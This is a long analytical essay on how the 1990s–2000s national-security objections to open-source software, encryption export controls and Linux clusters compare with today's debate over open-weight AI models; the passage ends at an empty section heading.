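# National-Security Objections to Open-Source Software and Whether They Apply to Open-Weight AI

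## What was published, who objected, and what they feared

Open-source software is published with its source code, the human-readable text of a program, under a licence that lets anyone run, change and share it. From the mid-1990s to the mid-2000s, American officials, software companies and think tanks argued that some or all of this software put national security at risk because hostile states and terrorists could download it too. People now make the same argument about open-weight AI models, which anyone can download, run and modify.

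The dispute over open-source software is two or three decades old, and several predictions made during it are specific enough to check. How far the results apply to AI depends first on what a developer releases when publishing a program or a model.

### Source code and model weights

Programmers write software as text, called source code. A program called a compiler translates it into a compiled program (also called a binary or executable), which a computer can run but a person can barely read. Most commercial packages come without the source code, as Route Fifty's *SCO* (2004) explains. *Opening the Open Source Debate* (Brown, 2002) quotes David Wheeler, a specialist in open-source software, who compared source code to a blueprint and the compiled program to the building. Unlike a building, though, a compiled program costs almost nothing to make, and anyone with the source code can make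 it on an ordinary computer.

The licence sets out what a recipient may do. R Street's *Mapping the Open-Source AI Debate* traces the best-known licence to Richard Stallman, an MIT programmer who in 1983 started the GNU project to write a free operating system. His GNU General Public License, or GPL, followed in 1989. It lets people run a program for any purpose, study and adapt it, hand out copies and share their improvements. Anyone who passes the program on must make the source code available. Linus Torvalds began the Linux operating system in 1991 and released it under the GPL.

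The Open Source Definition, the ten criteria that the software industry uses to decide whether a licence is open source, forbids discrimination against persons, groups or purposes. A licence that excluded the North Korean army would therefore not qualify, although export law might still apply to whoever distributes the program.

A developer makes an AI model by running a long computation, called training, that adjusts billions of numbers until the model responds to inputs as the developer wants. These numbers, called the model weights, determine how the model turns input into output. Training compute is the total amount of calculation used to set them. The developer of an open-weight model posts the weights for download, usually without the training data. A closed model stays on servers that its developer or a partner controls, and customers can use it only through those servers.

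A person with enough hardware can download and run both Linux and Llama, the family of models that Meta has published since 2023. She can read the Linux source code and find where it checks a password. She can also open Llama's weights, but she will see only enormous tables of numbers, with no passage that explains why the model refuses one request and answers another.

A user can change both Linux and Llama. With Linux, she edits the source code and compiles it again. With Llama, she can fine-tune the model by training it a little further on her own examples, which takes far less computing than Meta spent on the original. Nobel, Rozenshtein and Sharma (2024), in *Open-Access AI*, mention one result of such changes, a version called "badLlama" that lacks the original's safeguards. They put the cost of removing safeguards at less than $200.

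Open-source software and open-weight models differ in whether an outsider can rebuild them from what is published. The Linux source contains everything a programmer needs to reproduce the program or adapt it to uses its developers never intended. Apple similarly built Darwin, the core of its operating systems, from other people's open-source code. A model's weights, however, do not contain its training data. Nobel and colleagues argue that even a brilliant outsider could not have used Llama 2 to build its much better successor, Llama 3, and they compare the attempt to recovering a recipe from a finished cake.

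This is why they object to the phrase "open-source AI". Llama 3.2's licence also barred companies with more than 700 million monthly users and prohibited certain uses. Both restrictions violate the Open Source Definition. CSET, a research centre at Georgetown University, likewise reserves "open-source" for models that meet all ten of the definition's criteria. "Open-weight" is more accurate because it means only that the model's weights are available.

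The missing recipe is a real limit for a state adversary, but one that is easy to overstate. A state adversary here is a government that the speaker treats as hostile, which in this debate mostly means China, Russia, Iran and North Korea as seen from Washington. Training is the expensive part of a model, and the weights are what it produces. Someone who downloads the weights cannot repeat the training, but does not need to repeat it to use the model.

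### Export controls, foreign availability and marginal risk

Several of the objections depend on export controls, which are rules requiring a government licence before listed goods, software or technology go to certain countries or foreign persons. The main US rules for goods with both civilian and military uses are the Export Administration Regulations (EAR), which the Commerce Department administers. The Bureau of Industry and Security's *Steps for Using the EAR*, in the version current in May 2026, starts from five facts about a transaction: what the item is, where it is going, who will receive it, what they will do with it, and whether anyone involved is supporting a weapons-proliferation project. The exporter finds the item on the Commerce Control List, notes the reason for control, and checks that reason against the destination on a chart of countries. If the cell contains an X, the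 exporter needs a licence unless an exception applies. Separate, stricter rules apply to embargoed countries such as North Korea.

All of this assumes that the exporter knows the customer. A programmer who posts a file on a public website knows what the item is but cannot answer the other questions for each person who downloads it. Under the published-information exclusion, most information and software already made public is not subject to US export controls, though encryption software is a partial exception.

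Foreign availability means that the controlled country can get an equivalent elsewhere or make it itself. The Bureau of Industry and Security's *Foreign Availability Determination Procedures and Criteria* sets a fairly demanding test. The foreign item must be of comparable quality and actually obtainable from a source outside the United States, in quantities large enough to make the American control ineffective. Congress states in the U.S. Code that controls by one country alone on items widely available abroad are generally less effective. A government can still choose to keep such controls. When President Clinton (1996), in *Administration of Export Controls on Encryption Products*, kept the controls on encryption, he found that exports could do harm "even where comparable products are or appear to be available" from foreign sources.

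Marginal risk is the harm a release adds beyond what the same actor could do without it. SATAN, a free program released in 1995, scanned computer networks for weaknesses. Andrew Brown (1995) reported in *California biker lets Satan ride out on the Internet* that every flaw it looked for was already public, but few people knew where to find the details. SATAN's marginal risk therefore came from the work it saved intruders, and was much less than the full harm of a break-in.

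### The five objections

The sources for the historical objections vary in weight. Louis Freeh (1996) objected to encryption in a prepared statement to a Senate committee, *Impact of Encryption on Law Enforcement and Public Safety*. Kenneth Brown objected to readable code in a white paper. The SCO Group, a Utah software company, sent a letter to all 535 members of Congress. Hicks (2004) describes the mailing in *SCO Goes to Washington in Linux Battle*, and both Tech Monitor and eWeek's *SCO Takes Fight to Capitol Hill* quote from the letter. The fear of foreign contributors comes from *Using Linux Software in Defense Systems Violates Every Principle of Security* (2004), a Green Hills Software press release about a speech by its own chief executive. The alarm over SATAN is recorded partly in press quotations and partly in a calmer technical bulletin, *A Look at SATAN* by Fisher (1995).

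| Date | Who objected | Claimed route from publication to harm | What the objector sold or was responsible for |
|---|---|---|---|
| March–April 1995 | A trade newspaper quoted by Andrew Brown; more mildly, John Fisher | Anyone can download SATAN; intruders point it at a network before its administrators do and get a list of ways in | The newspaper covered the industry; Fisher's team handled computer break-ins for the US Energy Department |
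| July 1996 | Louis Freeh | Unbreakable encryption spreads at home and abroad; investigators can no longer read seized files or intercepted messages | Directed the FBI |
| May–June 2002 | Kenneth Brown, Alexis de Tocqueville Institution | Federal agencies adopt software with public source code; attackers study it for vulnerabilities, flaws that let them make it do what its owner does not want | Ran a Washington think tank that took money from Microsoft |
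| January 2004 | Darl McBride, SCO Group | A North Korean expert downloads Linux, links personal computers into a "virtual supercomputer" and so gets computing power that US law restricts | Headed a company that claimed to own Unix code and was in court over Linux |
| April 2004 | Dan O'Dowd, Green Hills Software | Foreign agents contribute to Linux under false names and plant a backdoor, a hidden function that bypasses security; US weapons then run it | Headed a company that sold operating systems |

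Only the last three objections are to open source itself. Freeh objected to any encryption product that police could not open with a court order, whether a company sold it or a programmer gave it away. Critics of SATAN objected to releasing one particular tool to everybody at once. The other objections belong in the list because each describes a way free publication supposedly arms an enemy, and each has a close counterpart in the debate about AI.

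### What the objectors had to gain

Three of the five objectors were competitors of open-source software or had ties to one. SCO was already in litigation with IBM when McBride wrote to Congress in early January 2004, and it sued Novell later that month. SCO claimed that Linux contained its Unix code. O'Dowd told a defence-industry forum that the Pentagon should prefer operating systems designed for the strictest security evaluation. Green Hills sold operating systems, and its press release named two suppliers of Linux for similar devices. The Alexis de Tocqueville Institution sold no software, but eWeek's *White Paper Attacks GPL* described it as partly funded by Microsoft, and a Microsoft spokesman confirmed the funding to *Wired* (2002).

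O'Dowd's commercial interest gave him a reason to call Linux dangerous whether or not it was, so his claim alone tells us very little. Plenty of people at the time looked no further than that interest, but it does not show that Linux was safe. Whether a foreign agent can slip code into an operating system depends on how its maintainers review contributions, not on who raises the question. A competitor may even be the first to notice a real weakness, since looking for one is part of the job. The journalist Declan McCullagh (2002) got this about right in *Terrorists could use open source software to wreak havoc!*, when he forwarded the Tocqueville Institution's press release to his mailing list. He wrote that Microsoft's money did not necessarily mean that Microsoft dictated the institution's opinions, though he still called the release "pretty silly".

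Supporters of open source had interests too. The Open Source and Industry Alliance, which answered SCO most sharply, was an association of companies with a stake in open source. In the AI debate, both sides are also suspected of self-interest. CSET quotes the AI researcher Andrew Ng's complaint that large companies lobby for licensing rules because they would prefer not to compete with open source. Meta, the most vocal corporate advocate of openness in 2024, was defending its own product. Freeh had nothing to sell, but encryption threatened his agency's wiretaps and searches, which is a reason to check his claims as well.

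### Two different fears

People on both sides often treat two fears as a single "security risk of open source": that adversaries will use what we publish, and that we will come to depend on what adversaries can read or write.

Some objectors feared what adversaries would do with the published software, and others feared what would happen if the government depended on it. The two fears can be told apart by asking whether the harm would still happen if the US government ran none of the software. A drug smuggler's encrypted telephone would still defeat a wiretap, McBride's North Korean would still have his supercomputer, and SATAN could still probe a federal network that had never installed it. These three objections express the fear of use. Brown and O'Dowd feared dependence. If the government did not run the code, Brown's attacker would learn nothing about its systems from reading it, and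 O'Dowd's foreign agent would be planting backdoors in somebody else's computers. The two fears are easy to confuse. The Tocqueville Institution's press release opens with terrorists, which suggests a fear of use, but they gain only "if the federal government attempts to switch" to open source, which is a fear of dependence.

The fears call for different remedies. If the worry is how others will use what is published, the obvious response is to restrict publication, and the case for doing so depends on whether equivalents are available abroad and how much risk publication adds. If the worry is the government's own dependence on what is published, it can leave publication alone and be more careful about what it buys, inspects and installs. *Defense Priorities in the Open-Source AI Debate* (Dahlgren 2024) reports that Army smartphones, Navy warships and missile-warning satellites were all running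 systems derived from Linux by 2024, so the dependence on open-source software that O'Dowd wanted to prevent already exists.

With AI, a remedy for one fear may make the other worse. CSET lists among the main risks of open models that adversaries can adapt an American model without the resources to build one. Dahlgren asks whether Chinese open models would replace American ones if Washington stopped American companies from publishing weights for that reason. If they did, American firms and agencies that wanted an open model would be building on one trained by a Chinese developer, which would raise O'Dowd's concern again.

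Both camps in the AI dispute now cite this history. Mark Zuckerberg, Meta's chief executive, has argued that open models will overtake closed ones, as Linux overtook the closed versions of Unix, and be at least as safe. The Centre for the Governance of AI, a research organisation, accepts that publishing source code has brought "substantial net benefits" for most software, but argues that some highly capable models may be dangerous enough to be exceptions. In Dahlgren's view, whether export controls on open models would help depends on whether the better precedent is the control of nuclear weapons exports or the old bans on public-key cryptography, which now protects online banking.

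## Encryption code treated as a weapon

Dahlgren weighs the export controls on cryptography as a precedent. Until the end of 1996, the US government held that an American who put a strong encryption program on a public website was exporting a weapon and needed a licence.

Encryption scrambles a message using an algorithm, which is a mathematical procedure, and a key, which is a secret number. Someone who intercepts the message without the key must either find a flaw in the algorithm or try keys until one works. The National Security Agency (NSA) intercepts foreign communications for the US government, and strong encryption could prevent it from reading what it collects.

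William Crowell, the NSA's deputy director, told a court in 1995 that the spread of cryptographic products would make it "easier" for the targets of American spying to keep vital information from the United States. The U.S. District Court for the District of Columbia quotes his statement in *Karn v. US Dept. of State* (1996). The Ninth Circuit's *Bernstein v. USDOJ* (1999) reproduces a declaration by William Lowell, who ran the State Department office that licensed arms exports. His examples of such information included military messages on the battlefield and aboard submarines, and the communications of terrorists and drug smugglers.

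Both men said "easier", a modest claim that is hard to refute. A navy with its own code-makers did not need free American software, but the software might change the habits of people who would otherwise have sent their messages unencrypted, or with weak protection, because strong encryption was too much trouble. Freeh's complaint about unreadable files and telephone calls also applied to Americans at home, but no law limited the encryption they could use among themselves, so export rules were the government's main means of control.

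### From the Munitions List to the 40-bit key

The Arms Export Control Act let the president draw up a list of military goods, the Munitions List, and control their export. The State Department put cryptographic software in category XIII of this list, which also included tanks, in category VII. According to the Congressional Research Service's *Encryption Export Controls*, an exporter had to register with the government and then obtain a licence, and the NSA advised on how the export would affect national security. The law did not require officials to consider whether the customer could get the same thing elsewhere, and no court could review their decision that a product belonged on the list.

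Disclosing encryption software to a foreigner inside the United States also counted as "export," so a researcher could in principle break the law by talking at a conference in California.

In practice the State Department generally let companies sell encryption abroad if the key was only 40 bits long. A key of *n* bits has 2^*n* possible values, so a 40-bit key has about 1.1 trillion. A machine that tests a billion keys a second could try them all in 18 minutes. The US government's standard for unclassified data, the Data Encryption Standard, used 56-bit keys. The same machine would need a little over two years to try all of those, but a thousand such machines would need less than a day. Trying every 128-bit key would take one machine about 10^22 years, and adding more machines would not make the search practical. The 40-bit limit therefore gave foreign customers some protection against an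 amateur but almost none against the NSA.

American customers often got the weak version too. Software companies complained that they could not sensibly build separate products for home and abroad.

At the end of 1996, the Bureau of Export Administration's *Encryption Items Transferred From the U.S. Munitions List* (1996) moved commercial encryption to the Commerce Control List. Encryption was no longer officially a weapon, but it remained harder to export than other software. The usual exceptions for programs that were already public or available from foreign sources did not apply. The new rules also explicitly treated posting encryption software on the internet as an export, unless the publisher took precautions against downloads from abroad.

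The Clinton administration let companies export encryption with keys of any length if the product allowed a third party to hold a spare key that investigators could obtain, an arrangement called key recovery. Companies could also export 56-bit products without a spare key if they promised to develop a recovery system within two years. Few people wanted to buy products with key recovery, and in 1998 the administration dropped the requirement to make that promise.

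### A book may leave the country, a diskette may not

By then strong encryption had been publicly available for years. In June 1991 Phil Zimmermann, a programmer in Colorado, released Pretty Good Privacy, or PGP, free, with its source code. PGP used public-key encryption, in which each person publishes one key and keeps a matching one private, so strangers can exchange encrypted messages without first agreeing on a secret. Copies reached the internet and went abroad almost immediately. Federal investigators spent about three years considering whether Zimmermann had illegally exported a munition. They dropped the case in January 1996 without charging him, so no court decided whether he had.

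MIT Press had meanwhile published PGP's source code as a printed book. In 1997, the source code of a later version left the United States legally as printed books, which volunteers in Europe scanned and turned back into a working program.

Philip Karn, a network engineer, challenged this distinction between paper and disk. In early 1994 he asked the State Department whether he could export *Applied Cryptography*, a textbook by Bruce Schneier that prints the source code of several strong encryption algorithms. The department said yes. A week later he asked about a diskette containing the same code, and the department classified it as a munition. After losing two appeals within the department, he sued.

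Judge Charles Richey ruled against Karn in March 1996. Richey was willing to assume that source code was speech, but found that officials were regulating what the diskette could do rather than any idea on it. Karn had argued that the algorithms were already available abroad, but Richey said the president had made a foreign-policy judgment that the court would not examine. He also thought it rational to treat the diskette differently from the book, because Karn had conceded that using the printed code took more time and effort. On that reasoning, the diskette's marginal risk came from saving people the work of typing or scanning the code.

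An appeals court sent the case back in 1997 after the rules had changed, and a new judge ordered a hearing on whether producing a working program from the diskette differed from producing one from the printed page. The government lifted its restrictions on such code before the courts decided, and Karn let his case lapse. In *The Applied Cryptography Case* (2000), he wrote that "for all practical purposes I got everything I wanted".

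Daniel Bernstein brought a more ambitious case over a program he wrote as a doctoral student at Berkeley. He had noticed that the rules controlled encryption but not hash functions, which reduce an input to a short value of fixed length. His program, Snuffle, showed how to build an encryption system around a hash function. The source code filled fewer than four printed pages and left out the hash function, so it could not encrypt anything until the reader supplied one. The State Department told him he needed a licence to export the program, an English version of its instructions, or the academic paper describing the method. It dropped the requirement for the paper after he sued in 1995.

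Judge Marilyn Patel ruled for Bernstein, and on 6 May 1999 the Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western states, upheld her decision by two votes to one. The majority held that cryptographers use source code to express ideas, much as mathematicians use equations. The licence requirement was therefore a prior restraint, a rule requiring official permission before speaking. American courts allow such rules only with tight safeguards. The licence requirement let officials refuse any export they thought inconsistent with national security or foreign policy, set no deadline once an application reached the president, and barred applicants from going to court. The government did not argue that publishing Snuffle would directly and immediately endanger the country, so the judges did not have to weigh that claim.

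This opinion did not settle the law, though people still cite it as if it had. The court withdrew it on 30 September 1999, in *Bernstein v. United States Department Of Justice* (1999), so that a larger panel could rehear the case. The government then changed the rules, and the rehearing never took place. Bernstein challenged the new rules too. *The Bernstein Cryptography Case Is Dismissed* (2003) recounts that a government lawyer assured Patel in October 2002 that officials would not enforce several parts of them. She dismissed the case the following year without deciding whether the rules were constitutional. According to the Civil Rights Litigation Clearinghouse's *Bernstein v. U.S. Department of Justice*, she held that he lacked standing and told him he could come back if officials ever threatened him with enforcement.

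Peter Junger, a law professor in Ohio, wanted to post encryption programs on his course website. The Commerce Department told him that he could export a printed textbook chapter containing encryption code, but that the electronic version would need a licence if it contained controlled software. A district court ruled against him in 1998, calling source code "inherently functional". The Sixth Circuit reversed that judgment in *Junger v. Daley* (2000), holding that the First Amendment protects source code. It added that national security can outweigh this protection, but that the government must show that the harms are "real, not merely conjectural" and that the rule will actually reduce them. The judges did not say whether the encryption rules met this test, and sent the case back to the district court to consider under the new regulations.

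Of the two appellate rulings, only the one in Junger's case survived, and it is narrower than the slogan "code is speech" suggests. Neither court considered anything like model weights, and the Ninth Circuit expressly left open even the status of compiled programs.

### Foreign products and the end of the controls

The courts mostly avoided the question of whether the controls worked, but two studies came closer to addressing it. The National Research Council's *Cryptography's Role in Securing the Information Society* (1996) urged the government to encourage the widespread use of cryptography, which protects businesses and public agencies as well as criminals. Kenneth Dam, a former deputy secretary of state, chaired the committee, whose members came from law, intelligence and computer science. They recommended letting companies export DES and gradually relaxing the other controls without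 abolishing them. The committee thought that widespread use of cryptography was "inevitable in the long run" and that its advantages outweighed its disadvantages.

The other study, *Growing Development of Foreign Encryption Products* (Hoffman, Balenson and colleagues, 1999), counted encryption products already being made outside the United States, updating a survey begun in 1993. The researchers sent out a call on mailing lists and searched trade publications and the web. They found 805 products from 35 countries, up from 656 products from 29 countries in December 1997. Britain made 139 and Germany 104, and Russia and Iran also made some. At least 167 used algorithms stronger than DES. The researchers judged foreign and American products to be of comparable quality on average.

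Americans for Computer Privacy, a coalition that campaigned against the controls, paid for part of this work. Only about a fifth of the products were confirmed as strong, and DES no longer offered serious protection. In 1998, a machine built by the Electronic Frontier Foundation, a digital-rights group, had found a DES key in under three days. The product count also doesn't show how many people used them. An earlier study by the Commerce Department and the NSA had found that American software still dominated world markets and that some foreign products might be weaker than advertised.

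A buyer who cared about secrecy could plainly get it without American help, so the controls did not keep strong encryption from a competent foreign government. But this doesn't refute the more careful argument for the controls, that most people use whatever comes with their computer. If the encryption built into American browsers was weak, much of the world's traffic stayed readable, whatever a specialist firm in Zurich might sell. Richey had made a version of this point in Karn's case, when he observed that without the restriction foreign intelligence targets would have more products to choose from.

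Some customers noticed the weaker encryption in American products and bought from foreign firms instead. Hoffman and colleagues quote an official advisory committee on the German firm Brokat, which offered German banks stronger encryption than they could get in American browsers and took half the European market for internet banking.

By 1999 the controls had few supporters outside the security agencies. A House bill to relax them had 258 co-sponsors, a majority of the chamber, although two committees rewrote it to keep strict controls. The Ninth Circuit ruled in May, the survey appeared in June, and the administration agreed to relax the controls in September. It is hard to say which of these pressures mattered most, but the survey was probably not decisive on its own, since officials had conceded for years that foreign products existed.

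The new rules took effect on 14 January 2000. After a government technical review, companies could now export encryption of any key length to private customers everywhere except seven countries that the State Department listed as supporters of terrorism. They could also sell retail products to foreign governments. Source code that anyone could read became, in Karn's words, "effectively freely exportable", and the Commerce Department reportedly wrote to Bernstein in February that he could post his program. According to the Bureau of Export Administration's *2001 Foreign Policy Report* (2001), the government still kept its advance reviews, its reporting requirements and its power to examine sales of strong encryption to foreign governments and armed forces.

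### What the agencies lost, and what the controls cost

The objectors were right that encryption would spread and that agencies would lose access to some messages. The best regular public figures come from the annual *Wiretap Report* of the Administrative Office of the U.S. Courts. For 2000, the year of the liberalisation, officials reported encountering encryption in 22 wiretaps and obtaining the readable text in all of them. They first reported failures in 2012, in four wiretaps. In 2016, when judges authorised about 3,200 wiretaps, officials encountered encryption in 125 and failed to break it in 101.

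These figures cover court-ordered wiretaps in American criminal cases. They leave out locked telephones, seized disks, and the NSA's interception of foreign communications, which was the main reason for the export controls. They also leave out wiretaps that investigators never requested because they expected to hear nothing useful. The true loss is certainly larger than the count, but nobody outside the agencies can say by how much.

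PGP had been free to download for nine years when officials reported no failures. Failures became common only after telephone makers and messaging companies began encrypting everything automatically. This timing fits the careful version of the officials' argument, that the danger lay in strong encryption becoming the default. It gives much less support for treating a mathematician's four pages of source code as a munition.

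The controls also did damage that surfaced only in 2015. In the 1990s, American browsers came in a full-strength version for domestic users and an export version with 40-bit keys. Websites had to serve both, so the protocol that secures web connections had the browser list the kinds of encryption it could handle and the server pick one. Some of these options were export-grade. After 2000 hardly anyone needed the export-grade options, but programmers left them in the software so that old machines would still work.

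FREAK, an attack that researchers in France and at Microsoft announced in March 2015, exploited these leftovers. The attacker sits between a browser and a website, such as on a café's wireless network, and changes the browser's opening message to request export-grade encryption. The server replies with a 512-bit public key. (Public keys have to be much longer than the secret keys described above to be equally strong, and 512 bits is weak.) The browser should reject a key it never requested, but a bug made several widely used browsers accept it. The attacker then works out the two prime numbers whose product forms the key, which took a few hours and about $100 of rented computing, and can read the traffic. When the researchers checked, more than a third of web servers with trusted certificates still offered export-grade keys, including the one for the NSA's public website.

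Two months later another group described Logjam, an attack on a different way of agreeing on a key. In this method, called Diffie–Hellman, both computers calculate with the same large prime number. The flaw was in the protocol itself, so even browsers without FREAK's bug were exposed. Breaking a 512-bit prime took about a week of computing, but nearly all of that work depends only on the prime, and most vulnerable servers used the same one. After the first week, an attacker could break each new connection that used this prime in about a minute.

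A rule meant to keep foreigners' messages readable thus exposed Americans' messages fifteen years after its repeal. Browser makers and website operators share the blame, since they had all that time to delete the old options. Neither discovery came with evidence that criminals had used the flaw, so the known harm is exposure rather than theft. Still, the officials of the 1990s were wrong to assume that they could weaken encryption only for foreigners, because Americans used the same network.

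### Encryption compared with a frontier model

Encryption mainly protects the person who uses it. A smuggler can encrypt his messages to hide them from the police, but the program does not help him break into anyone else's computer, and it also protects bank customers from criminals. A frontier model (one of the most capable AI models of its time) can help its user defend himself too, but it can also be used against other people, for example to search a stranger's software for vulnerabilities. The National Research Council judged that the benefits of wide use outweighed the harms for a largely defensive tool, so anyone who wants to apply that conclusion to models has to make a new case for it.

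Publishing a way to break codes is different from publishing a way to make them. In December 2026 Anthropic and OpenAI (2026), two American AI developers, announced that they had found weaknesses in some of the cryptography that protects the internet, with help from unreleased models, and would not publish their methods. The companies withheld the methods voluntarily, after consulting the US government on what to disclose, so some objections to publishing cryptographic research are still accepted.

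The comparison is closer on foreign availability, since other countries train capable models, just as 35 of them made encryption products in 1999. But once nobody can search all the keys, a stronger cipher gains its user almost nothing, so a Swiss algorithm with a 128-bit key was as good as any American one. Models have no obvious point at which more ability stops being useful. A foreign model that is somewhat worse than the best American one is a partial substitute, and how good a substitute depends on the task and changes with every release. Brokat's success carries over most directly from this history, because a customer who cannot get the American product will take a foreign one that is good enough.

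Encryption programs and model weights differ most in the cost of making an equivalent. A competent programmer could write an encryption program from a textbook, or type one in from a printed page, which is why Karn could make the rules look ridiculous. Nobody could do that with a model, because 70 billion weights of two bytes each would fill 56 million pages at 2,500 bytes to a page. Even a reader with a full description of how the developer trained the model would still have to pay for the training compute. A government that stopped a developer from publishing weights would therefore be withholding something that most foreign groups could not make for themselves, which was never true of PGP. Once the weights are on the internet, however, anyone can copy them as easily as people copied PGP in 1991, and no later change in the licence rules will bring them back.

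## Free software as a way around computer export controls

The United States had separate export rules for encryption software and for fast computers. In a letter to every member of Congress dated 8 January 2004, Darl McBride complained that free software let a hostile state get the effect of a fast computer without buying one. The government had stopped trying to keep encryption source code in the country four years earlier.

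### McBride's letter and the replies

McBride's example was a North Korean expert who downloads Linux from the internet and turns some ordinary PCs into a virtual supercomputer. HITB's *Linux threatens US security, SCO tells Congress* (2004) reprints the fullest version of McBride's sentence, in which Linux is "complete with multiprocessing capabilities misappropriated from Unix". McBride argued that export licensing had kept commercial software away from hostile countries, and that the GPL let them have the equivalent anyway.

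In the letter, McBride warned of threats to the American software industry, the country's competitive position and, last, national security. He proposed no law. "There wasn't even a call to action", a company spokesman said in CRN's *Open-Source Activists Protest SCO, Microsoft Anti-Linux Lobbying*, and eWeek reported that SCO had drafted no bill. SCO executives had, however, met several federal agencies to argue against purchasing policies that favoured open source. If this was the remedy, it would not have addressed the security threat, because people in Pyongyang could still have downloaded Linux even if federal agencies bought Unix instead.

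The word "misappropriated" came from SCO's lawsuits. In March 2003 SCO sued IBM for $1 billion, later raised to $3 billion, alleging that IBM had put Unix code into Linux. Route Fifty pointed out that SCO had itself sold a version of Linux under the GPL. Novell, an earlier owner of the Unix business, denied that it had ever sold SCO the copyrights and, according to LWN's *Report from the SCO front*, registered them in its own name. A jury sided with Novell in 2010, when SCO was already bankrupt. IBM settled SCO's suit against it in 2021 for $14.25 million.

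Ownership of the code did not affect whether a North Korean could run it. McBride also seems to have picked the wrong feature. Multiprocessing usually means several processors in one machine sharing its memory. Linked PCs each run their own copy of the operating system and exchange messages over a network, so single-processor PCs without any multiprocessing code would have been enough.

Rick Boucher, a Democratic congressman from Virginia, called the argument "absurd on its face". He told eWeek that every software exporter was under the same controls, and that anyone willing to break the law could do it as easily with SCO's products. Ed Black, who ran the Open Source and Industry Alliance, said the same in the alliance's published reply, and added that American export controls could cover all software only if foreigners were prevented from writing any. USENIX (2004), an association of computing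 researchers and system administrators, objected in an open letter in February that McBride had confused copyright licensing with export policy, and that neither body of law depended on whether a program was free.

Boucher was right about the law. *Letter to the US Department of Commerce on Exporting Linux to Iraq*, published in Linux Journal, explains that the relevant licence exception let people export open-source software to all but seven countries, one of which was North Korea. The letter also objects that Linux faced tighter rules for Iraq than commercial operating systems did.

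But this hardly answers McBride. SCO could refuse an order from North Korea, but anyone can download software from a volunteer's public site without placing an order. USENIX nearly conceded this when it noted that export officials had acknowledged they could not restrict where most software went. Black's remark about foreign programmers was the stronger reply. Torvalds began Linux in Helsinki, and SUSE, one of the main commercial versions, came from Germany. The US government could have slowed Linux down by stopping Americans from contributing, but North Korea could still have downloaded what everyone else wrote.

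### Adding up personal computers

The United States limited computer exports by MTOPS, or millions of theoretical operations per second, a rating that exporters calculated from a machine's design without timing it on a real job. The government sorted countries into four tiers. From January 2002, exporters needed a licence to ship a computer rated above 190,000 MTOPS to a third-tier country such as China, Russia or India. Fourth-tier countries, including North Korea, Iran and Iraq, could buy essentially no high-performance computers from American firms.

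A cluster is a group of networked computers that work on parts of the same problem. Thomas Sterling and Donald Becker built the best-known early example, Beowulf, at NASA in 1994 from 16 PCs running Linux. Other laboratories copied the design, including Clemson University, which called its version Grendel.

A cluster can get around a speed limit by combining computers that each fall well below it. The government chose a limit of 190,000 MTOPS because officials expected companies to start selling servers with 32 of Intel's Itanium processors, which would rate close to that, or a little under 6,000 MTOPS per processor. If a good PC of 2004 rated 5,000 MTOPS, the ratings of 38 PCs would add up to the limit.

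This sum leaves out the time the PCs spend communicating over the network. One PC might take a second to advance a simulation of air flowing over a wing by one time step. If the air is divided into 38 blocks, one for each PC, each machine finishes its block in about 26 milliseconds. But the air at the edge of one block pushes on the air in the next, so the PCs must exchange their edge values before any of them can start the next step. If the exchange takes 10 milliseconds, each step takes about 36, and the cluster is about 27 times as fast as one PC instead of 38 times.

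If one PC needs time *W* for a step, and *n* PCs need time *c* to exchange results, then

speed-up = *W* / (*W*/*n* + *c*).

If *W* is one second and *c* is 10 milliseconds, 62 PCs can match a single machine rated at 190,000 MTOPS. If *c* is 30 milliseconds, no number of PCs is enough, because the exchange alone takes longer than the 26 milliseconds the single machine needs for the whole step. Real networks usually perform worse than this formula predicts, because the exchange tends to slow down as more machines join.

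Some calculations barely use the network. In a search for an encryption key, each PC can check its own range of keys and report back only if it finds the right one, so 38 PCs can search 38 times as fast as one. The value of McBride's virtual supercomputer therefore depended heavily on what the North Korean wanted to calculate.

Virginia Tech had just shown that his basic idea was sound. In November 2003 its cluster of 1,100 Apple desktop machines, linked by a fast commercial network, placed third on the TOP500, a twice-yearly ranking of the world's fastest publicly known computers. The cluster reached 58 per cent of its theoretical speed on the ranking's test, which involves solving a very large set of equations.

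Those machines ran Apple's operating system, and Cornell University had been running a 256-processor cluster on Microsoft Windows since 1999. Linux was cheaper and easier to adapt, and most cluster builders preferred it, but a government already evading an embargo to get PCs would have been willing to use a pirated copy of Windows. The marginal risk of Linux was therefore limited to the money and trouble it saved such a government compared with using pirated Windows.

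### What the auditors had already found

Congress already knew about clusters when SCO raised them. In the mid-1990s, a Stanford team led by Seymour Goodman concluded that controlling computers below 7,000 MTOPS would cost too much and become steadily less effective. The General Accounting Office (GAO), Congress's auditor, relayed this finding in 1998.

Two years later, GAO's *Export Controls* (2000) more bluntly called the system "ineffective", because it controlled individual machines and could not prevent a country from linking many uncontrolled ones. The limit for China and Russia was then 28,000 MTOPS, and people had already built clusters of about 70,000 MTOPS from parts anyone could buy. Analysts at Lawrence Livermore, a US nuclear weapons laboratory, warned that ignoring clusters created "a false sense of security". An Indian computing centre that the US government had blacklisted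 over weapons proliferation was advertising its own cluster design.

Officials at Los Alamos, another weapons laboratory, told the auditors that clusters were harder to operate than to build. Running one meant scheduling hundreds of separate jobs and moving data between the machines, their disks and long-term storage. Manufacturers supplied software for this with a finished supercomputer, but the owner of a home-made cluster had to do much of it by hand.

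By 2002 government departments disagreed about how much clustering mattered. The State Department held that it had made fast computers impossible to control effectively, while a Defense Department analysis from October 2001 had concluded that a cluster was not comparable to a single high-performance machine. GAO's *Export Controls* (2002) reports both positions and criticises the decision to raise the limit from 85,000 to 190,000 MTOPS, partly because the higher limit would save countries from having to build clusters. Officials had also justified the increase by predicting that ten companies would soon sell machines at the new level, but GAO found only one that did.

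The two departments were probably thinking of different calculations. State was right about key searches, and Defense had a point about tightly connected simulations, at least with the networks of the time.

Computers at or below the 190,000 MTOPS threshold could meet 98 per cent of the Pentagon's military computing needs. The agency that runs the American nuclear weapons programme thought that machines with an effective performance of just 10,000 MTOPS would significantly help Chinese weapons designers. On paper, two of the PCs in the example reach that level. By 2004, then, the threshold no longer separated harmless computers from dangerous ones. Defense officials told GAO that they had based it on the market and on what they thought they could still control.

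A fast computer is also of little use without people who know what to calculate. Goodman, Peter Wolcott and Patrick Homer studied military uses of these computers in 1998 and concluded that neither they nor the American government had enough information to say which countries could use them productively for particular purposes. McBride's example assumes that the North Korean already has expertise, PCs and an internet connection before the download begins, which is nearly everything the country might have lacked.

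The MTOPS rating eventually stopped being useful for export control. Intel rates the Pentium Gold G5600, a processor for inexpensive desktop PCs, at 212,550 MTOPS, so a single chip now exceeds the limit that McBride's expert needed a cluster to reach. The Commerce Department no longer asks exporters to calculate the rating.

### Linux in China, Iran and North Korea

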